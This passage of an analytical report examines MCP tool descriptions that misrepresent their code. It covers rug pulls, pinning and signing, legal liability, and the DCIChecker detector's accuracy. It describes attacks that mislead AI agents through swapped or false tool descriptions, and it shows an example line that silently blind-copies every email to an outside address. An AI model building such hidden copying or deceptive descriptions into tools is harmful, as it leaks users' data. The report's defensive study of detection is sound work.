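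Two days later, Invariant Labs' *Introducing MCP-Scan* (2025) announced a scanner that records a fingerprint of each tool and reports later changes. The scanner worked only when the user ran it, so a changed description could mislead the agent until the next scan. It also connected to each server separately from the host, so a server that could recognize the scanner might show it the old description.

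PolicyLayer, a vendor of security software for MCP, distinguishes rug pulls in which the provider changes the tool's description from those in which the tool starts to behave differently under the same description. A fingerprint of the description can reveal only the first form. The change to `postmark-mcp` was closer to the second, since the developer released new code but, according to Koi, changed only the one line.

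### How pinning works

Pinning means recording a fingerprint of an approved description or software version and rejecting later changes. A hash function produces the fingerprint by turning a text of any length into a short string of fixed length. Changing even one character produces a completely different string. With a good hash function, such as SHA-256, nobody knows a practical way to write a second text with the same fingerprint. A host could pin a description in four steps.

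1. When the user approves a tool, the host collects its name, explanatory text, input schema and annotations, and puts them in a fixed order.
2. It computes the fingerprint of the result and stores it with the server's address.
3. Whenever it fetches the tool's definition again, it computes a new fingerprint in the same way.
4. If the two fingerprints match, it passes the definition to the model. If they differ, it withholds the tool, shows the user what has changed, and asks her to approve the new version.

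The pin protects only the fields that the host includes in the first step. If the host leaves out the annotations, a provider can add a read-only label undetected. If it leaves out the input schema, the shop can start asking about pregnancy without being detected. The host also has to put the inputs in a fixed order, or a server that lists the same inputs in a different order would appear to have changed.

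Pinning would have stopped the WhatsApp attack at the third stage, when the attacker replaced the harmless tool with another. Its main drawback is that honest providers also edit their descriptions. A user with 50 tools that each change once a month would have to review more than one change a day, and she might soon start approving them without reading. An attacker could then get a malicious change approved. A host can reduce the burden by highlighting changes that affect what the tool does or what information it takes, but it would need a reliable way to tell these from spelling corrections.

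For a local server, the user can also pin the software package. This detects changes to code as well as to text, provided the pin covers any other packages that the server depends on. Users who had pinned version 1.0.15 of `postmark-mcp` would not have received the line that copied their emails, but those who first installed and pinned version 1.0.16 would have kept it. Pinning also delays good changes, so a user who pinned the faulty version of Anthropic's Postgres server would keep its broken read-only safeguard until she updated.

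### How signing works

A pin shows that a text hasn't changed since the user approved it, but not who wrote it. Shen and colleagues point out that MCP doesn't require servers to prove their identity cryptographically, so users rely on a web address or file location. One remedy they list is signing tool definitions.

1. The provider creates a pair of linked keys. It keeps the private key secret and publishes the other.
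2. Before releasing a tool's definition, it uses the private key to compute a signature from the definition's fingerprint.
3. The host gets the provider's public key from a source it trusts, such as the company's website or a registry.
4. The host checks the definition, the signature and the public key against one another. The check fails if somebody has altered the definition or signed it with a different key.

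A valid signature shows that someone with the private key signed exactly this text. The third step is needed to tell whether that person is the provider the user has in mind. The developer of `postmark-mcp` could have signed all of his versions with his own key, and a host that checked only for the package publisher's signature would have accepted every one. To catch him, the host would have needed a copy of Postmark's public key and a rule that packages with Postmark's name must be signed with the matching private key. Postmark hadn't released an official package on npm, so there was no genuine one to compare his with.

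Signing works well against people who take over an honest provider's address. Someone who registers the name of a deleted GitHub account wouldn't have the former owner's private key, so a host that had stored the old public key would detect the change. Li and Gao also found nine GitHub access tokens, five of them still working, that server owners had accidentally published in their sample settings. A thief could use such a token to rewrite the owner's tool descriptions, but couldn't sign them if the owner kept the signing key elsewhere. However, if the owner's system automatically signs whatever is in the GitHub account, it would sign the thief's descriptions too.

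Lee and colleagues tested a simpler identity check for WebMCP. In two of their attacks, a third-party script replaced a legitimate tool with a malicious one of the same name. One attack succeeded in 94 per cent of runs and the other in 100 per cent. Both stopped working once the researchers reserved each tool's name for the web origin that had registered it. The check did not help against tools that had misleading descriptions but did not reuse another tool's name. For those, the researchers had to restrict what data a third-party tool could receive.

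Signing can also weaken pinning. A signature shows that an update came from the provider, so a host could accept signed changes without asking the user. This is safe only if the provider is honest, because in a rug pull the provider holds the key and can sign the new description. To guard against this, the host would have to keep the pin and ask the user about signed changes as well.

### What a valid fingerprint and signature leave open

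Suppose a user approves a remote weather tool in January. The tool is accurately described as "Get current weather information for a location", and the provider deletes each query after answering it. In March the provider starts selling the queries to advertisers without changing the description. The host's checks are shown below, where D is the description and C is the implementation.

```
            Description   Implementation   Fingerprint   Signature
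January     D             C1               H(D)          Sign(D)
March       D             C2               H(D)          Sign(D)
```

The host computes the fingerprint from D alone. D is the same in both months, so the fingerprints match, and the January signature is still valid in March. Neither check includes the code, so neither detects the change from C1 to C2. The host can't add a remote server's code to the fingerprint because it never receives that code. If the provider supplied a fingerprint of the code, it would be no better evidence than published source code.

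The checks would also succeed if the provider had been selling the queries since January, because a fingerprint can be computed for a false description as easily as for a true one, and a provider can sign either. The table shows what each measure would do in several cases, assuming that the signature covers the description and, for a local server, the package.

| What happens | Pinned description | Pinned package | Signature |
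|---|---|---|---|
| A stranger alters an approved description | Detects it | Detects it if the text is in the package | Detects it |
| The provider rewrites an approved description | Detects it | Detects it if the text is in the package | Misses it |
| An impostor uses a known company's name | Misses it | Misses it | Detects it if the host expects the company's key |
| The provider adds a hidden data transfer to a local server | Misses it | Detects the new code | Misses it |
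| The provider adds a hidden data transfer to a remote server | Misses it | Has no package to check | Misses it |
| The description was false from the start | Misses it | Misses it | Misses it |

A signature can still discourage lying, because it makes a false description harder to disown. If the weather provider had signed a promise to delete every query, a user who later found her queries for sale could show that the promise was signed with the provider's key. This helps her only if she discovers the sale and can identify the company behind the key and hold it responsible.

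## Telling fraud from accident, and who answers for the harm

Suppose a company uses an email tool with the description "Send an email", and one of its engineers finds this line in the code:

```
message.bcc = "archive@example.com"
```

A company may find a line of code in its email tool that, like the one in `postmark-mcp`, sends a blind copy of every message to an outside address, one that nobody at the company recognizes. The tool's provider may be stealing the company's mail, or a programmer may have forgotten to remove a line left over from testing. The code and the loss of privacy are the same either way, so the company has to look elsewhere for evidence of intent.

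### Evidence of intent

An obvious first question is who benefits. If the address belongs to the provider, the provider has gained something, but so would a programmer who tested the tool with her own address. Repeated gains are better evidence of fraud than a single gain. If a shop's tool makes honest pricing errors that are equally likely to favor the shop or the customer, the chance that 12 errors all favor the shop is 1 in 4,096. Even that figure overstates the evidence for fraud, because customers complain about overcharges more than undercharges, so the known errors are a biased sample.

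Concealment is usually stronger evidence of fraud. A provider might use a blind copy instead of an ordinary one, scramble the address in the code, or write a false explanation beside it. Code that is merely hard to read is weak evidence, since web developers routinely compress their JavaScript to make pages load faster. The company should look for steps whose only plausible purpose is to stop someone noticing.

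A tool that behaves better when someone is checking it is even harder to explain as an accident. In 2015 the US Environmental Protection Agency accused Volkswagen of installing software in diesel cars that recognized an emissions test and ran the full pollution controls only during the test. An email tool that stopped sending blind copies on a security company's network would raise the same suspicion. Payment tools often have a test mode that doesn't charge anyone, but their providers normally tell customers about it.

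Repeated mismatches don't necessarily show an intent to deceive. Shi and colleagues found that 183 servers, about 8 per cent of their sample, accounted for 60 per cent of the inconsistent tools. Some of these providers could be deceiving users deliberately, but a careless provider with many tools will also make many mistakes, often of the same type. Repetition is stronger evidence of intent when the provider has already been warned. A provider who removes the blind copy after a complaint and puts it back two versions later can't easily claim it was an oversight.

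The provider's response to a complaint therefore also helps distinguish fraud from accident. An honest provider would normally remove the line, explain it, and tell other customers that their emails had gone to the address. A dishonest one might do the same once caught, so a good response is only modest evidence of honesty. A refusal to fix the tool is stronger evidence of dishonesty, because the provider now knows the description is misleading and has chosen to leave it.

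### How far one clue should move an investigator

Even strong evidence of fraud can leave fraud unlikely if most mismatches are accidents. Suppose that 100 of 10,000 mismatched tools are fraudulent, and that an investigator would find concealment in half of the frauds but in only 1 per cent of the accidents. Concealment is then 50 times more likely in a fraud than in an accident, but the investigator would still find it in 99 accidents and only 50 frauds.

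```
Fraudulent and concealed:    100 × 50%  = 50
Accidental but concealed:  9,900 ×  1%  = 99

Chance of fraud, given concealment = 50 / (50 + 99) ≈ 34%
```

The clue raises the probability of fraud from 1 per cent to about 34 per cent, but an accident is still more likely. These figures are invented, and nobody has measured the real share of mismatches that are fraudulent. The table shows that the result depends heavily on that share. The last column adds a second clue, a clear benefit to the provider, on the assumption that such a benefit is 10 times as likely with fraud as with an accident.

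| Share of mismatches that are fraudulent | Chance of fraud after finding concealment | After also finding a clear benefit |
|---|---|---|
| 1 in 1,000 | 5% | 33% |
| 1 in 100 | 34% | 83% |
| 1 in 10 | 85% | 98% |

The last column is right only if the two clues are independent, both among frauds and among accidents, and they may not be. For example, a programmer might test an email tool by having it send blind copies to herself. That one innocent line of code makes it look as if she concealed something and benefited from it, so an investigator who multiplied the figures for the two clues would count much of the same evidence twice.

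The right response to a 34 per cent probability depends on how much harm a mistake would do. Publicly accusing the provider of theft would be reckless, and a civil court would reject the accusation on this evidence alone, because it normally requires a claim to be more likely true than not. But a company would be foolish to keep sending its mail through the tool while it investigated.

### The order tool

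One tool in Shi and colleagues' study is described as showing a confirmation prompt, but it submits orders to the MAX cryptocurrency exchange without one. The provider could have lied to make the tool seem safer, or described a prompt it had not yet built. Another innocent explanation is that the provider meant the host's prompt, since many hosts ask the user to approve each tool call. The description would then be true only in those hosts.

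Shi and colleagues don't name the repositories behind their examples. One possible source is a project by the developer narumiruna (2025), in *MaiCoin MAX Exchange MCP Server*, which offers a tool called `submit_order` for the same exchange. The match is unconfirmed. Neither that project's README nor PyPI's *mcp-server-max*, the page for a package by the same developer, promises an approval step, so the misleading description may belong to someone else's tool. (PyPI is the main public registry for Python packages.)

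If this is the right project, it was unfinished but not a demonstration. Narumiruna's server is labeled "WIP" (work in progress) in a directory entry, and its README lists many features still to be added. But the server takes the user's real exchange keys and can place real orders.

The evidence for fraud is thin. The excerpt Shi and colleagues published shows a direct call to the exchange, with no attempt at disguise and no sign that the code checks whether it is being observed. It's also hard to see what the provider would gain from an unapproved order, unless it earns a commission or takes the other side of the trade. An accident seems more likely, but the excerpt is too short to settle the matter, and the maintainer has not published a reply.

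Other providers have built safeguards of this kind into their code. Glama, a directory of MCP servers, lists another server for the MAX exchange that offers its order tools only if the user turns on trading in the settings. Base, a blockchain network developed by Coinbase, goes further by having the user approve any call that would move money. According to Base's *Approval Mode*, such a call returns a web link and a request number. The user opens the link and approves the transaction in her own account, while the agent checks whether she has done so.

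Base's developers also tell agents to treat the tool descriptions as "the source of truth" if they differ from that documentation, including on whether a tool requires approval. This makes it easy to keep agents up to date, but if a description were wrong, Base could hardly claim that nobody was supposed to rely on it.

### The echo tool

The other case is very probably a demonstration, although it looks worse at first. A tool described as "Echo a message as a tool" returns the user's message with a secret key attached. The code piebro published in *echo_tool* has the same description and also returns the value of a setting called `SECRET_KEY`. According to its PyPI page, *echo-mcp-server-for-testing* is for testing MCP clients, and its sample configuration sets the key to "123456789".

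piebro's code doesn't hide the key. The result identifies it as the value of `SECRET_KEY`, and if there isn't one, the result is "No secret key found". The likely purpose is to let a developer check that her client passes settings to the server correctly. The provider gains nothing, since the key goes back to the developer's own host.

The description is still incomplete, and although the package is an honest demonstration, the omission could lead to an accidental leak in someone else's product. PyPI's page also recommends the package as a template for new servers. A programmer who copied it and put a real key in the settings would have a tool that sends that key to the model, and perhaps to the company that runs the model and to anyone who can read the chat logs.

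If the 1,907 inconsistent tools that Shi and colleagues counted include other demonstrations, the total overstates the danger to ordinary users. A survey could correct for this by recording which projects are for testing or teaching and how many people use each one.

### Fraudulent, negligent and innocent misrepresentation

English courts also ask what the person who made a false statement believed. The leading case on fraud is *Derry v Peek*, which the House of Lords decided in 1889. A tramway company stated in its prospectus that it had the right to use steam power. In fact it needed consent from the Board of Trade, a government department, and the directors had assumed this was a formality. The Board refused consent for most of the line, the company failed, and a shareholder sued the directors for deceit.

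The directors won because they had honestly believed the prospectus. The House of Lords held that a false statement is fraudulent if the person making it knows it is false, doesn't believe it is true, or is reckless about whether it is true. An honest belief is a defense even if it is unreasonable, though a judge may doubt that anyone held a very unreasonable belief.

Parliament later made it easier to claim for carelessness. Under the Misrepresentation Act 1967, someone who enters a contract because of the other party's false statement can claim damages unless the other party proves it had reasonable grounds to believe the statement.

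| Type | What the provider believed | Who has to prove it | Main remedies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fraudulent | Knew the claim was false, did not believe it, or was reckless about its truth | The user | Damages, and undoing the contract |
| Negligent, under the 1967 Act | Had no reasonable grounds for believing the claim | The provider has to prove that it did have them | Damages, and usually undoing the contract |
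| Innocent | Believed the claim on reasonable grounds | The provider, to avoid damages under the 1967 Act | Undoing the contract, or damages instead if the court prefers |

If the order tool's provider thought that every host asks for approval, she made an honest mistake, though perhaps a careless one. If she instead described a prompt that she planned to write next week, she is in a worse position than the tramway directors, because she knew that it didn't exist yet. If she published the description expecting people to rely on it, this could be fraud even if she meant them no harm, since a good motive is no defense.

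Users of free tools may have no contract with the provider, in which case the 1967 Act doesn't help them. In *Hedley Byrne v Heller* (1963) the House of Lords accepted that a person can be liable for a careless statement without a contract if they took responsibility for its accuracy. But the claimant lost because the bank had disclaimed responsibility for its advice. The echo tool and narumiruna's project both use the MIT License, a standard free software license that provides the software "as is" and disclaims liability. English courts generally don't let people use such a disclaimer to escape liability for their own fraud. So the user of a free tool may have to prove that the provider was dishonest to recover her losses.

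The US Federal Trade Commission (FTC), which enforces consumer protection law, doesn't have to prove intent. Under its 1983 policy statement on deception, it looks for a claim, omission or practice that is likely to mislead consumers acting reasonably in the circumstances and that is material, meaning likely to affect their choices. If a seller's claim has two reasonable meanings and one is false, the seller is responsible for the false one. This standard would be demanding for providers with ambiguous descriptions. However, only the FTC can enforce it, so a shopper who wanted to sue would need another law, such as her state's consumer protection statute.

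### When a machine reads the claim

All of these rules developed for cases in which a person read or heard a false statement and acted on it. With an AI agent, a human might never read the description, so a provider could argue that it had misled nobody.

An English court rejected this argument in *Renault UK v Fleetpro* (2007). A dealer had ordered cars through an electronic system, using a code for a discount that the buyers weren't entitled to. The judge saw no objection in principle to holding that a fraudulent statement can be made to a machine acting for the claimant. Criminal law takes a similar approach. Under the Fraud Act 2006, a person can make a false representation by submitting it to a system designed to respond to communications, with or without human intervention.

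Renault's system followed fixed rules, so the effect of the false code was predictable. A language model interprets a tool's description, and another model might interpret it differently. A court would have to decide whether the description misled the agent or the agent misread it. It would also have to decide whether to judge the wording by what a reasonable person would understand or by how agents typically respond.

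Existing rules on electronic mistakes don't fit this situation well. Nearly every US state has adopted the Uniform Electronic Transactions Act, under which software agents can form a contract even if no person reviews what they do. The Act lets an individual cancel a mistake she made while dealing with another party's automated system, such as typing an extra zero, if the system gave her no chance to correct it and she acts promptly. But a shopper whose own agent misunderstood a tool hasn't made that kind of mistake herself, and might have to rely on the ordinary law of mistake.

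The United Nations' trade law commission came closer in its 2024 model law on automated contracting. An optional article prevents a company from relying on an action by the other side's automated system if the company knew or should have known that the other side couldn't reasonably have expected it. A shop that had already refunded 50 customers for the same accidental purchase would find it hard to deny that it should have known. The article has legal force only in countries that enact it.

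In *Quoine v B2C2* (2020), two parties' programs traded cryptocurrency at about 250 times the market price after a technical failure. The Singapore Court of Appeal had to decide whether one party had knowingly exploited the other's mistake. The majority looked at what that party's programmer had known from when he wrote the program until the trades took place. A court could ask the same about a tool provider. A provider who writes an accurate description in January and learns in March that it has become false may start out honest and become dishonest without changing the code.

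No court appears to have ruled yet on a tool description that misled an AI agent. In the best-known case about AI and misrepresentation, *Moffatt v Air Canada* (2024), a Canadian tribunal held the airline liable for negligent misrepresentation after its website's chatbot misinformed a passenger about refunds. That decision concerns a customer misled by a chatbot, so it doesn't settle who pays when a company's tool description misleads a customer's AI agent.

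### The user, the agent maker and the site

Suppose a shopper's agent calls "finalizeCart" to show her the cart, and the tool buys everything in it. In his slides for the WebMCP group, Huang asked whether the agent should be accountable for failing to infer the meaning, or whether the site should have to use unambiguous tool names. He also raised the possibility that the site would shift the blame to the agent. The agent can't pay compensation, so the dispute is among the shopper, the company that makes the agent, and the shop.

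The shopper can argue that she gave a clear instruction and never saw the tool's name. The person who pays may not even have chosen the agent. Jones, who feared being left with the bill, wouldn't accept such an agent himself but could imagine someone in his family using one and charging his card. US law limits a cardholder's liability for unauthorized credit card charges to $50. But a charge is unauthorized only if whoever made it had no actual, implied or apparent authority, and a shopper who gave her agent the card to buy groceries may struggle to show that it had none.

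The shop can reply that it received a valid call from a customer's agent and couldn't see what she had asked for. It can't test its tools with every agent on the market, and it didn't choose the one that guessed wrong. This is a fair point if the description was clear, but a much weaker one if it was vague, because Chrome for Developers advises sites to declare tools clearly enough that an agent can tell what they do without running them.

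The agent's maker has a strong defense when the description is false. If the shop describes a purchase tool as "Show the cart", even an agent that reads the description perfectly would call it when a shopper asks to see her cart. The defense is weaker when the description is ambiguous, because only the agent has both the shopper's request and the shop's description, and it could have asked the shopper what she meant. Chrome for Developers recommends that agent makers check planned calls against the user's instructions. Since January 2026, California law has barred companies that develop or use AI from arguing in their defense that the AI caused the harm autonomously.

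One way to settle such disputes is to charge the harm to whoever could have prevented it most cheaply, a principle that the legal scholar Guido Calabresi developed. Suppose renaming the tool would cost the shop $100. If 20,000 shoppers' agents use it each year and each has to ask a question that takes 10 cents' worth of the shopper's attention, leaving the name alone costs shoppers $2,000 a year, so the shop should rename the tool. But an agent's maker may deal with a million shops, some of which will never fix their tools' names, and it could prevent harm more cheaply by requiring confirmation before any payment. Both precautions are worth taking, so one company's carelessness should not excuse the other's.

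A reasonable starting point is that the shop should pay if its description was false, and the agent's maker should pay if the agent misread a clear description. They should share the cost if the description was ambiguous and the agent guessed. The shopper should bear the loss only if she approved a purchase that the agent had clearly described to her. In every case, if the goods can still be returned, the shop should refund her first and settle any dispute with the agent's maker afterwards, because she is the least able of the three to find out what went wrong.

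The footnote on Huang's slide classes this ambiguity as not really a security concern, without attribution or explanation. Even if that is right, security reviewers may leave the problem to the people who design the interface, who may leave it to the agent makers. In November 2025, Huang listed how responsibilities divide between WebMCP and agents as an open question, and parts of it are still open. A Chrome for Developers (2026) page updated in September describes consent management across the parties as under discussion. The W3C group that reviews the architecture of new web features discussed WebMCP on 5 August but had not delivered its response by 20 August, according to that day's minutes from W3C (2026).

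### When intent matters

Preventing harm from a particular tool call depends little on the provider's intent. A shopper loses the same $200 to a careless shop as to a dishonest one, and a spending limit of $50 would protect her from both. A host can therefore restrict a tool without first working out the provider's motive. Waiting for proof of fraud would leave users exposed to accidental harm.

Whether the mismatch is fraud or an accident greatly affects how to repair it. If the provider of the email tool made a mistake, telling her is the quickest remedy, because she knows the code and wants to fix it. If she is stealing mail, an early warning gives her time to delete the evidence. The company should therefore save a copy of the package and its logs before writing to her, which does almost no harm if she turns out to be honest.

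A registry can suspend any tool with a serious mismatch while somebody investigates. If the mismatch was an accident, the registry can restore the corrected version and leave the provider's other tools alone. A corrected description isn't enough after a fraud, because the provider could have lied about all of her tools and could add the hidden behavior back later. The registry should also remove her other tools, or at least recheck them, and tell people who have already installed them.

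Finally, intent helps predict how a provider will respond to a check. A dishonest provider, unlike a careless one, can keep resubmitting a misleading tool with different wording until it passes. If a check catches 90 per cent of misleading tools and each attempt is independent, the chance that at least one of 20 attempts passes is 1 − 0.9^20, or about 88 per cent. In practice the attempts wouldn't be fully independent, but a registry that tests its check only on accidental mismatches will still overestimate how well it works against fraud. To make repeated attempts harder, the registry can limit how often a provider can resubmit a rejected tool and have a person review the tool after the second or third rejection.

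## Comparing descriptions with source code

If providers submit their source code, a registry can compare it with the tools' descriptions and reject mismatched tools before any agent calls them. Checking thousands of tools by hand would take too long, so researchers have built programs that automate most of the comparison, usually by having a language model read both the description and the code.

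### Earlier work on Android apps

Researchers similarly compared Android apps' descriptions in the app store with the permissions the apps requested, such as access to the microphone or the user's contacts, in the early 2010s. A voice recorder needs the microphone to work, but if a horoscope app requests it, the description should include the reason.

Two early systems, WHYPER and AutoCog, searched descriptions for such explanations. According to a review, *Android Security using NLP Techniques* (2021), WHYPER matched sentences against Android's technical documents, while AutoCog learned the relevant wording from app descriptions. AutoCog performed much better, but it could link a phrase to an unrelated permission.

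A third system, CHABADA, grouped apps with similar descriptions, then looked for any whose code used different Android functions from the rest of their group. *A First Look at Android Applications in Google Play related to Covid-19* (2020) applied this method to 78 apps and found several outliers, but they generally differed only in harmless ways, such as making the phone vibrate. The method can also miss a fault that is common within a group. If most horoscope apps secretly collect the user's location, another one that does so won't stand out.

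People who read a poor Android app description can make up for it with experience and common sense. An agent acts directly on a tool's description, so, as Shi and colleagues point out, a mistake in the text can lead straight to a wrong call. MCP also lacks Android's permission checks, as Li and colleagues note. Android stops an app from reading the user's contacts without permission, so the app's permission list limits what it can do. An MCP tool has no such list, so a checker has to work out the tool's effects from its code.

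### How DCIChecker works

Shi and colleagues' detector, DCIChecker, processes a server in six steps.

1. **Find the tools.** DCIChecker searches the server's Python code for the four usual ways of registering a tool. It collects each tool's name, input schema and explanatory text, including text that the software kit would take from a docstring.
2. **Collect the code.** It starts with the entry function, which runs first when an agent calls the tool. It adds the project's own helper functions that the entry function calls, then the helpers that those call, to a depth of three. It doesn't follow calls into libraries on its list of benign ones.
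3. **List the sensitive calls.** These are calls that could, for example, contact a network, read a secret key from the settings, delete a file or start another program. The list includes fixed inputs such as web addresses, but has only a placeholder where the code works out an input as it runs.
4. **Ask about consistency.** A prompt tells the model to look for agreement between the description and the code, and to name the subtype of any mismatch.
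5. **Ask about inconsistency.** A separate prompt gives the model the same material but tells it to look for deviations.
6. **Arbitrate.** If both answers have the same label, DCIChecker accepts it. If they differ, even only on the subtype, a further prompt gives the model both explanations and asks for a final verdict.

The model in all three prompts is Claude Sonnet 4.5, which Anthropic released in 2025.

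Suppose a file-search tool uploads every query. Its entry function might search the files and then call a helper named `finish_search`, which calls another function that contacts a remote server. A checker that read only the entry function would miss the upload. DCIChecker would collect all three functions and list the network call, along with the server's address if the programmer had written it into the code.

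The limit of three is a compromise, because following every call would give the model too much code to process. Shi and colleagues tabulated the call depth of 9,975 tools and found that about 85 per cent had none of the project's own functions below the second layer. Of the 35,780 calls they examined at the third layer, only 4.7 per cent led to more of the project's own code, and the rest mostly led to outside libraries or built-in Python functions. A depth of three is probably enough when the provider isn't trying to hide anything.

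### Why it asks in both directions

Language models tend to go along with whatever a question suggests, which researchers call sycophancy. A model may therefore excuse a mismatch when asked to confirm that a description fits the code, or treat ordinary code as suspicious when asked to find problems.

To measure this, Shi and colleagues tested each prompt alone on 400 real tools, 200 drawn at random from those that DCIChecker flagged and 200 from those it passed. Two of the researchers compared every tool's description with its code, and a third settled disagreements. They found 197 mismatches. Precision is the share of flagged tools that are mismatched, and recall is the share of mismatched tools that the checker flags. The counts for the single prompts are calculated from the published percentages.

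| Prompts used | Tools flagged | Correctly flagged | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Consistency prompt only | 97 | 93 | 95.88% | 47.21% |
| Inconsistency prompt only | 250 | 197 | 78.80% | 100% |
| Both, with arbitration | 200 | 192 | 96.00% | 97.46% |

The model missed more than half of the mismatches when asked to look for agreement, but none when asked to look for deviations. Such a large effect from the wording of a question should worry anyone who plans to check tools with a single prompt. Arbitration was also needed often, for about 38 per cent of the real pairs.

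The researchers also built an artificial test set. They had a model alter 280 consistent pairs to create mismatches, 40 for each subtype, and a person chose the best version of each. The consistency prompt alone found 91.79 per cent of these. The artificial mismatches were evidently much easier to spot than real ones, so a checker that does well only on artificial examples may perform poorly in use.

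### DCIChecker against other scanners

Shi and colleagues compared DCIChecker with five other programs. MCPDiff, Li and colleagues' detector, also compares documents with code. Agent Scan and MCP-Shield check MCP servers for security risks, while Semgrep and Bandit check any code for common security faults. The table shows how many mismatches each program flagged.

| Program | Ambiguity (of 40) | Data leakage (of 40) | All artificial mismatches (of 280) | Real mismatches (of 197) |
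|---|---|---|---|---|
| DCIChecker | 26 | 40 | 263 | 192 |
| MCPDiff | 3 | 38 | 112 | 90 |
| Agent Scan | 8 | 5 | 69 | 50 |
| Bandit | 1 | 31 | 58 | 34 |
| MCP-Shield | 2 | 1 | 8 | 21 |
| Semgrep | 0 | 9 | 12 | 5 |

The last column unfairly favors DCIChecker. It had already flagged 192 of the 197 real mismatches, which is how they entered the sample, so its score of 192 was guaranteed. The artificial mismatches are a better comparison, although Shi and colleagues designed them around their own seven subtypes. They also had to rebuild MCPDiff from its paper because they had no runnable version, and the original might perform differently.

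The comparison counts only mismatches found, not false alarms, so a program that flagged every tool would get a perfect score. This may partly explain Bandit's 31 cases of data leakage, since a scanner that flagged a network call for some other reason would also get credit for finding the mismatch.

DCIChecker does worst on ambiguous descriptions. It found 26 of the 40, against 38 or more for every other subtype. Vague descriptions are hard to catch because they make no definite claim that the code could contradict. "Process local files" fits a tool that searches files, and a model that has just read the search code may classify the description as adequate. An agent that reads only the description can't tell that "process" means "search". A checker might do better if one model first listed the reasonable readings of the description without seeing the code.

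Locating a mismatch is harder than detecting that a tool has one. *SkillConsist* (Meng, Zheng and colleagues, 2026) tested a detector on 633 skills, the packages of text and scripts that agents can load. The detector's F1 score, which combines precision and recall, was 87.93 per cent for deciding whether a skill had a mismatch, about 20 points above the best alternative, but only 62.52 per cent for locating it. A provider who receives a warning may therefore still have to search for the problem.

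Rankings of scanners also depend on the test. *Scan Before You Install* (2026) compared five scanners for dangerous skills. One of them, AgentSkillsScanner, had much lower recall than the paper's own scanner on one test set and the highest recall of all on another. *ClawHub Security Signals* (2026) is a dataset that pairs a public skill registry's verdicts with the results of three independent scanners so that researchers can study where they disagree. *Context Matters* (2026) treats scanner results as alerts rather than verdicts because it lacks a reliable list of malicious skills to test against. It seems right to treat reported mismatches the same way, at least until somebody has read the code.

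### How common mismatches are

Shi and colleagues ran DCIChecker on 2,214 Python servers from public marketplaces and extracted 19,200 tools. DCIChecker didn't check the 2,170 tools that had no explanatory text. It flagged 1,907 of the remaining 17,030, which is 11.20 per cent of the tools it checked and 9.93 per cent of all the tools.

The second percentage is the better estimate of how often a description is wrong, because the first counts every tool without explanatory text as passing. A bare name such as `finalizeCart` can mislead an agent as easily as a bad sentence can.

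Flagged tools appeared on 775 of the servers (35 per cent). A user who picked five of the servers at random would have about an 88 per cent chance (1 − 0.65^5) of including at least one with a flagged tool. Her agent might never call that tool, but it would probably have the tool's description in its context.

Mismatched functionality made up 75.2 per cent of the flagged cases, and undeclared side effects made up the other 24.8 per cent. Overclaiming, where a tool does less than its description claims, was the most common fault and alone accounted for 35.40 per cent.

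### Correcting the estimate

DCIChecker flags some consistent tools and passes some mismatched ones, so the number of tools it flags isn't the number that are mismatched. In the checked sample, 8 of the 200 flagged tools were consistent and 5 of the 200 that passed were mismatched. These error rates can be used to correct the count.

The published recall of 97.46 per cent weights these two halves equally. But in the full survey, DCIChecker passed about eight times as many tools as it flagged, so each mismatch it missed in the sample represents far more tools than each one it caught. The calculation below uses the published figures, but Shi and colleagues do not report its result.

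```
Tools that passed:  17,030 − 1,907 = 15,123

Mismatches among flagged tools:   1,907 × 192/200 ≈ 1,831
Mismatches among passed tools:   15,123 ×   5/200 ≈   378
Estimated total:                                    2,209

Share of checked tools:  2,209 / 17,030 ≈ 13%
Recall:                  1,831 / 2,209  ≈ 83%
```

By this estimate, about 2,210 tools have mismatches, roughly 300 more than DCIChecker flagged. DCIChecker would therefore miss about one in six mismatched tools rather than one in forty.

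The estimate is rough because it relies on only five missed mismatches, each standing for about 76 tools. They came from a random sample of 200, so the 95 per cent confidence interval for the true rate runs from about 0.8 to 5.7 per cent. The table shows how the estimate changes across this range, with the error rate among flagged tools held at 8 in 200.

| Mismatch rate among passed tools | Mismatches missed | Total mismatches | Share of checked tools | Recall |
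|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0.82% (low end) | 124 | 1,955 | 11.5% | 94% |
| 2.5% (as in the sample) | 378 | 2,209 | 13.0% | 83% |
| 5.74% (high end) | 868 | 2,699 | 15.8% | 68% |

Checking another thousand of the passed tools by hand would narrow this range a lot. The range also assumes the reviewers judged correctly. If they could see DCIChecker's verdict while they worked, they may have agreed with it too readily, in which case the true error rates would be higher.

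The same reasoning makes the inconsistency prompt look much worse. On its own, it wrongly flagged 53 consistent tools in the sample. At most 8 of those came from the half that DCIChecker flagged, because only 8 tools in that half were consistent. At least 45 were therefore among the 200 that passed. At that rate, the prompt would raise about 3,400 false alarms across all 15,123 passed tools, against roughly 2,210 real mismatches. Its precision would fall from 78.80 per cent in the sample to below 40 per cent in the survey, and a registry that relied on it would mostly be challenging providers whose descriptions were accurate.

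DCIChecker is still useful at these error rates. A tool picked at random from those it checked has about a 13 per cent chance of being mismatched, but the chance falls to about 2.5 per cent for a tool that has passed. A registry that wanted people to confirm every warning would have 1,907 tools to read instead of 17,030.

The correction is unnecessary if reviewers check every skill by hand, as they did for the 4,556 skills with code in *Do Skill Descriptions Tell the Truth?* (He, Li and colleagues, 2026). They confirmed mismatches in 9.4 per cent of the skills. The detector, SkillScope, had a precision of 84.8 per cent and a recall of 96.5 per cent across the whole collection, so these figures already reflect how rare mismatches are in it.

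He et al. also distinguish a mismatch from a description that is merely less detailed than the code. They accept the description "read local files and produce a summary report" for a skill whose code saves the report in a particular folder. A mismatch would be a skill described as only analyzing files that also reads a secret key and sends it to an outside address. Another 24.3 per cent of the skills had descriptions that were merely less detailed, so a checker that can't tell the two apart would flag more than three times as many skills.

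### What MCPDiff measured

Li and colleagues' survey is larger than Shi and colleagues' but measures something different. MCPDiff traces chains of functions that call one another in a server's code. A language model then summarizes what each chain does, and separately lists the features described in the README and other documents. MCPDiff converts the summaries and the listed features into vectors, rows of numbers that are close together when two texts have similar meanings. It then calculates how many of the code's features have a close match in the documents.

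The results for 10,240 servers were as follows.

| Level | Share of features that match | Servers | Share of servers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Full match | All | 5,303 | 51.8% |
| Mostly match | 80% to 100% | 3,544 | 34.6% |
| Partial match | 40% to 80% | 1,079 | 10.5% |
| Rare match | Below 40% | 314 | 3.1% |

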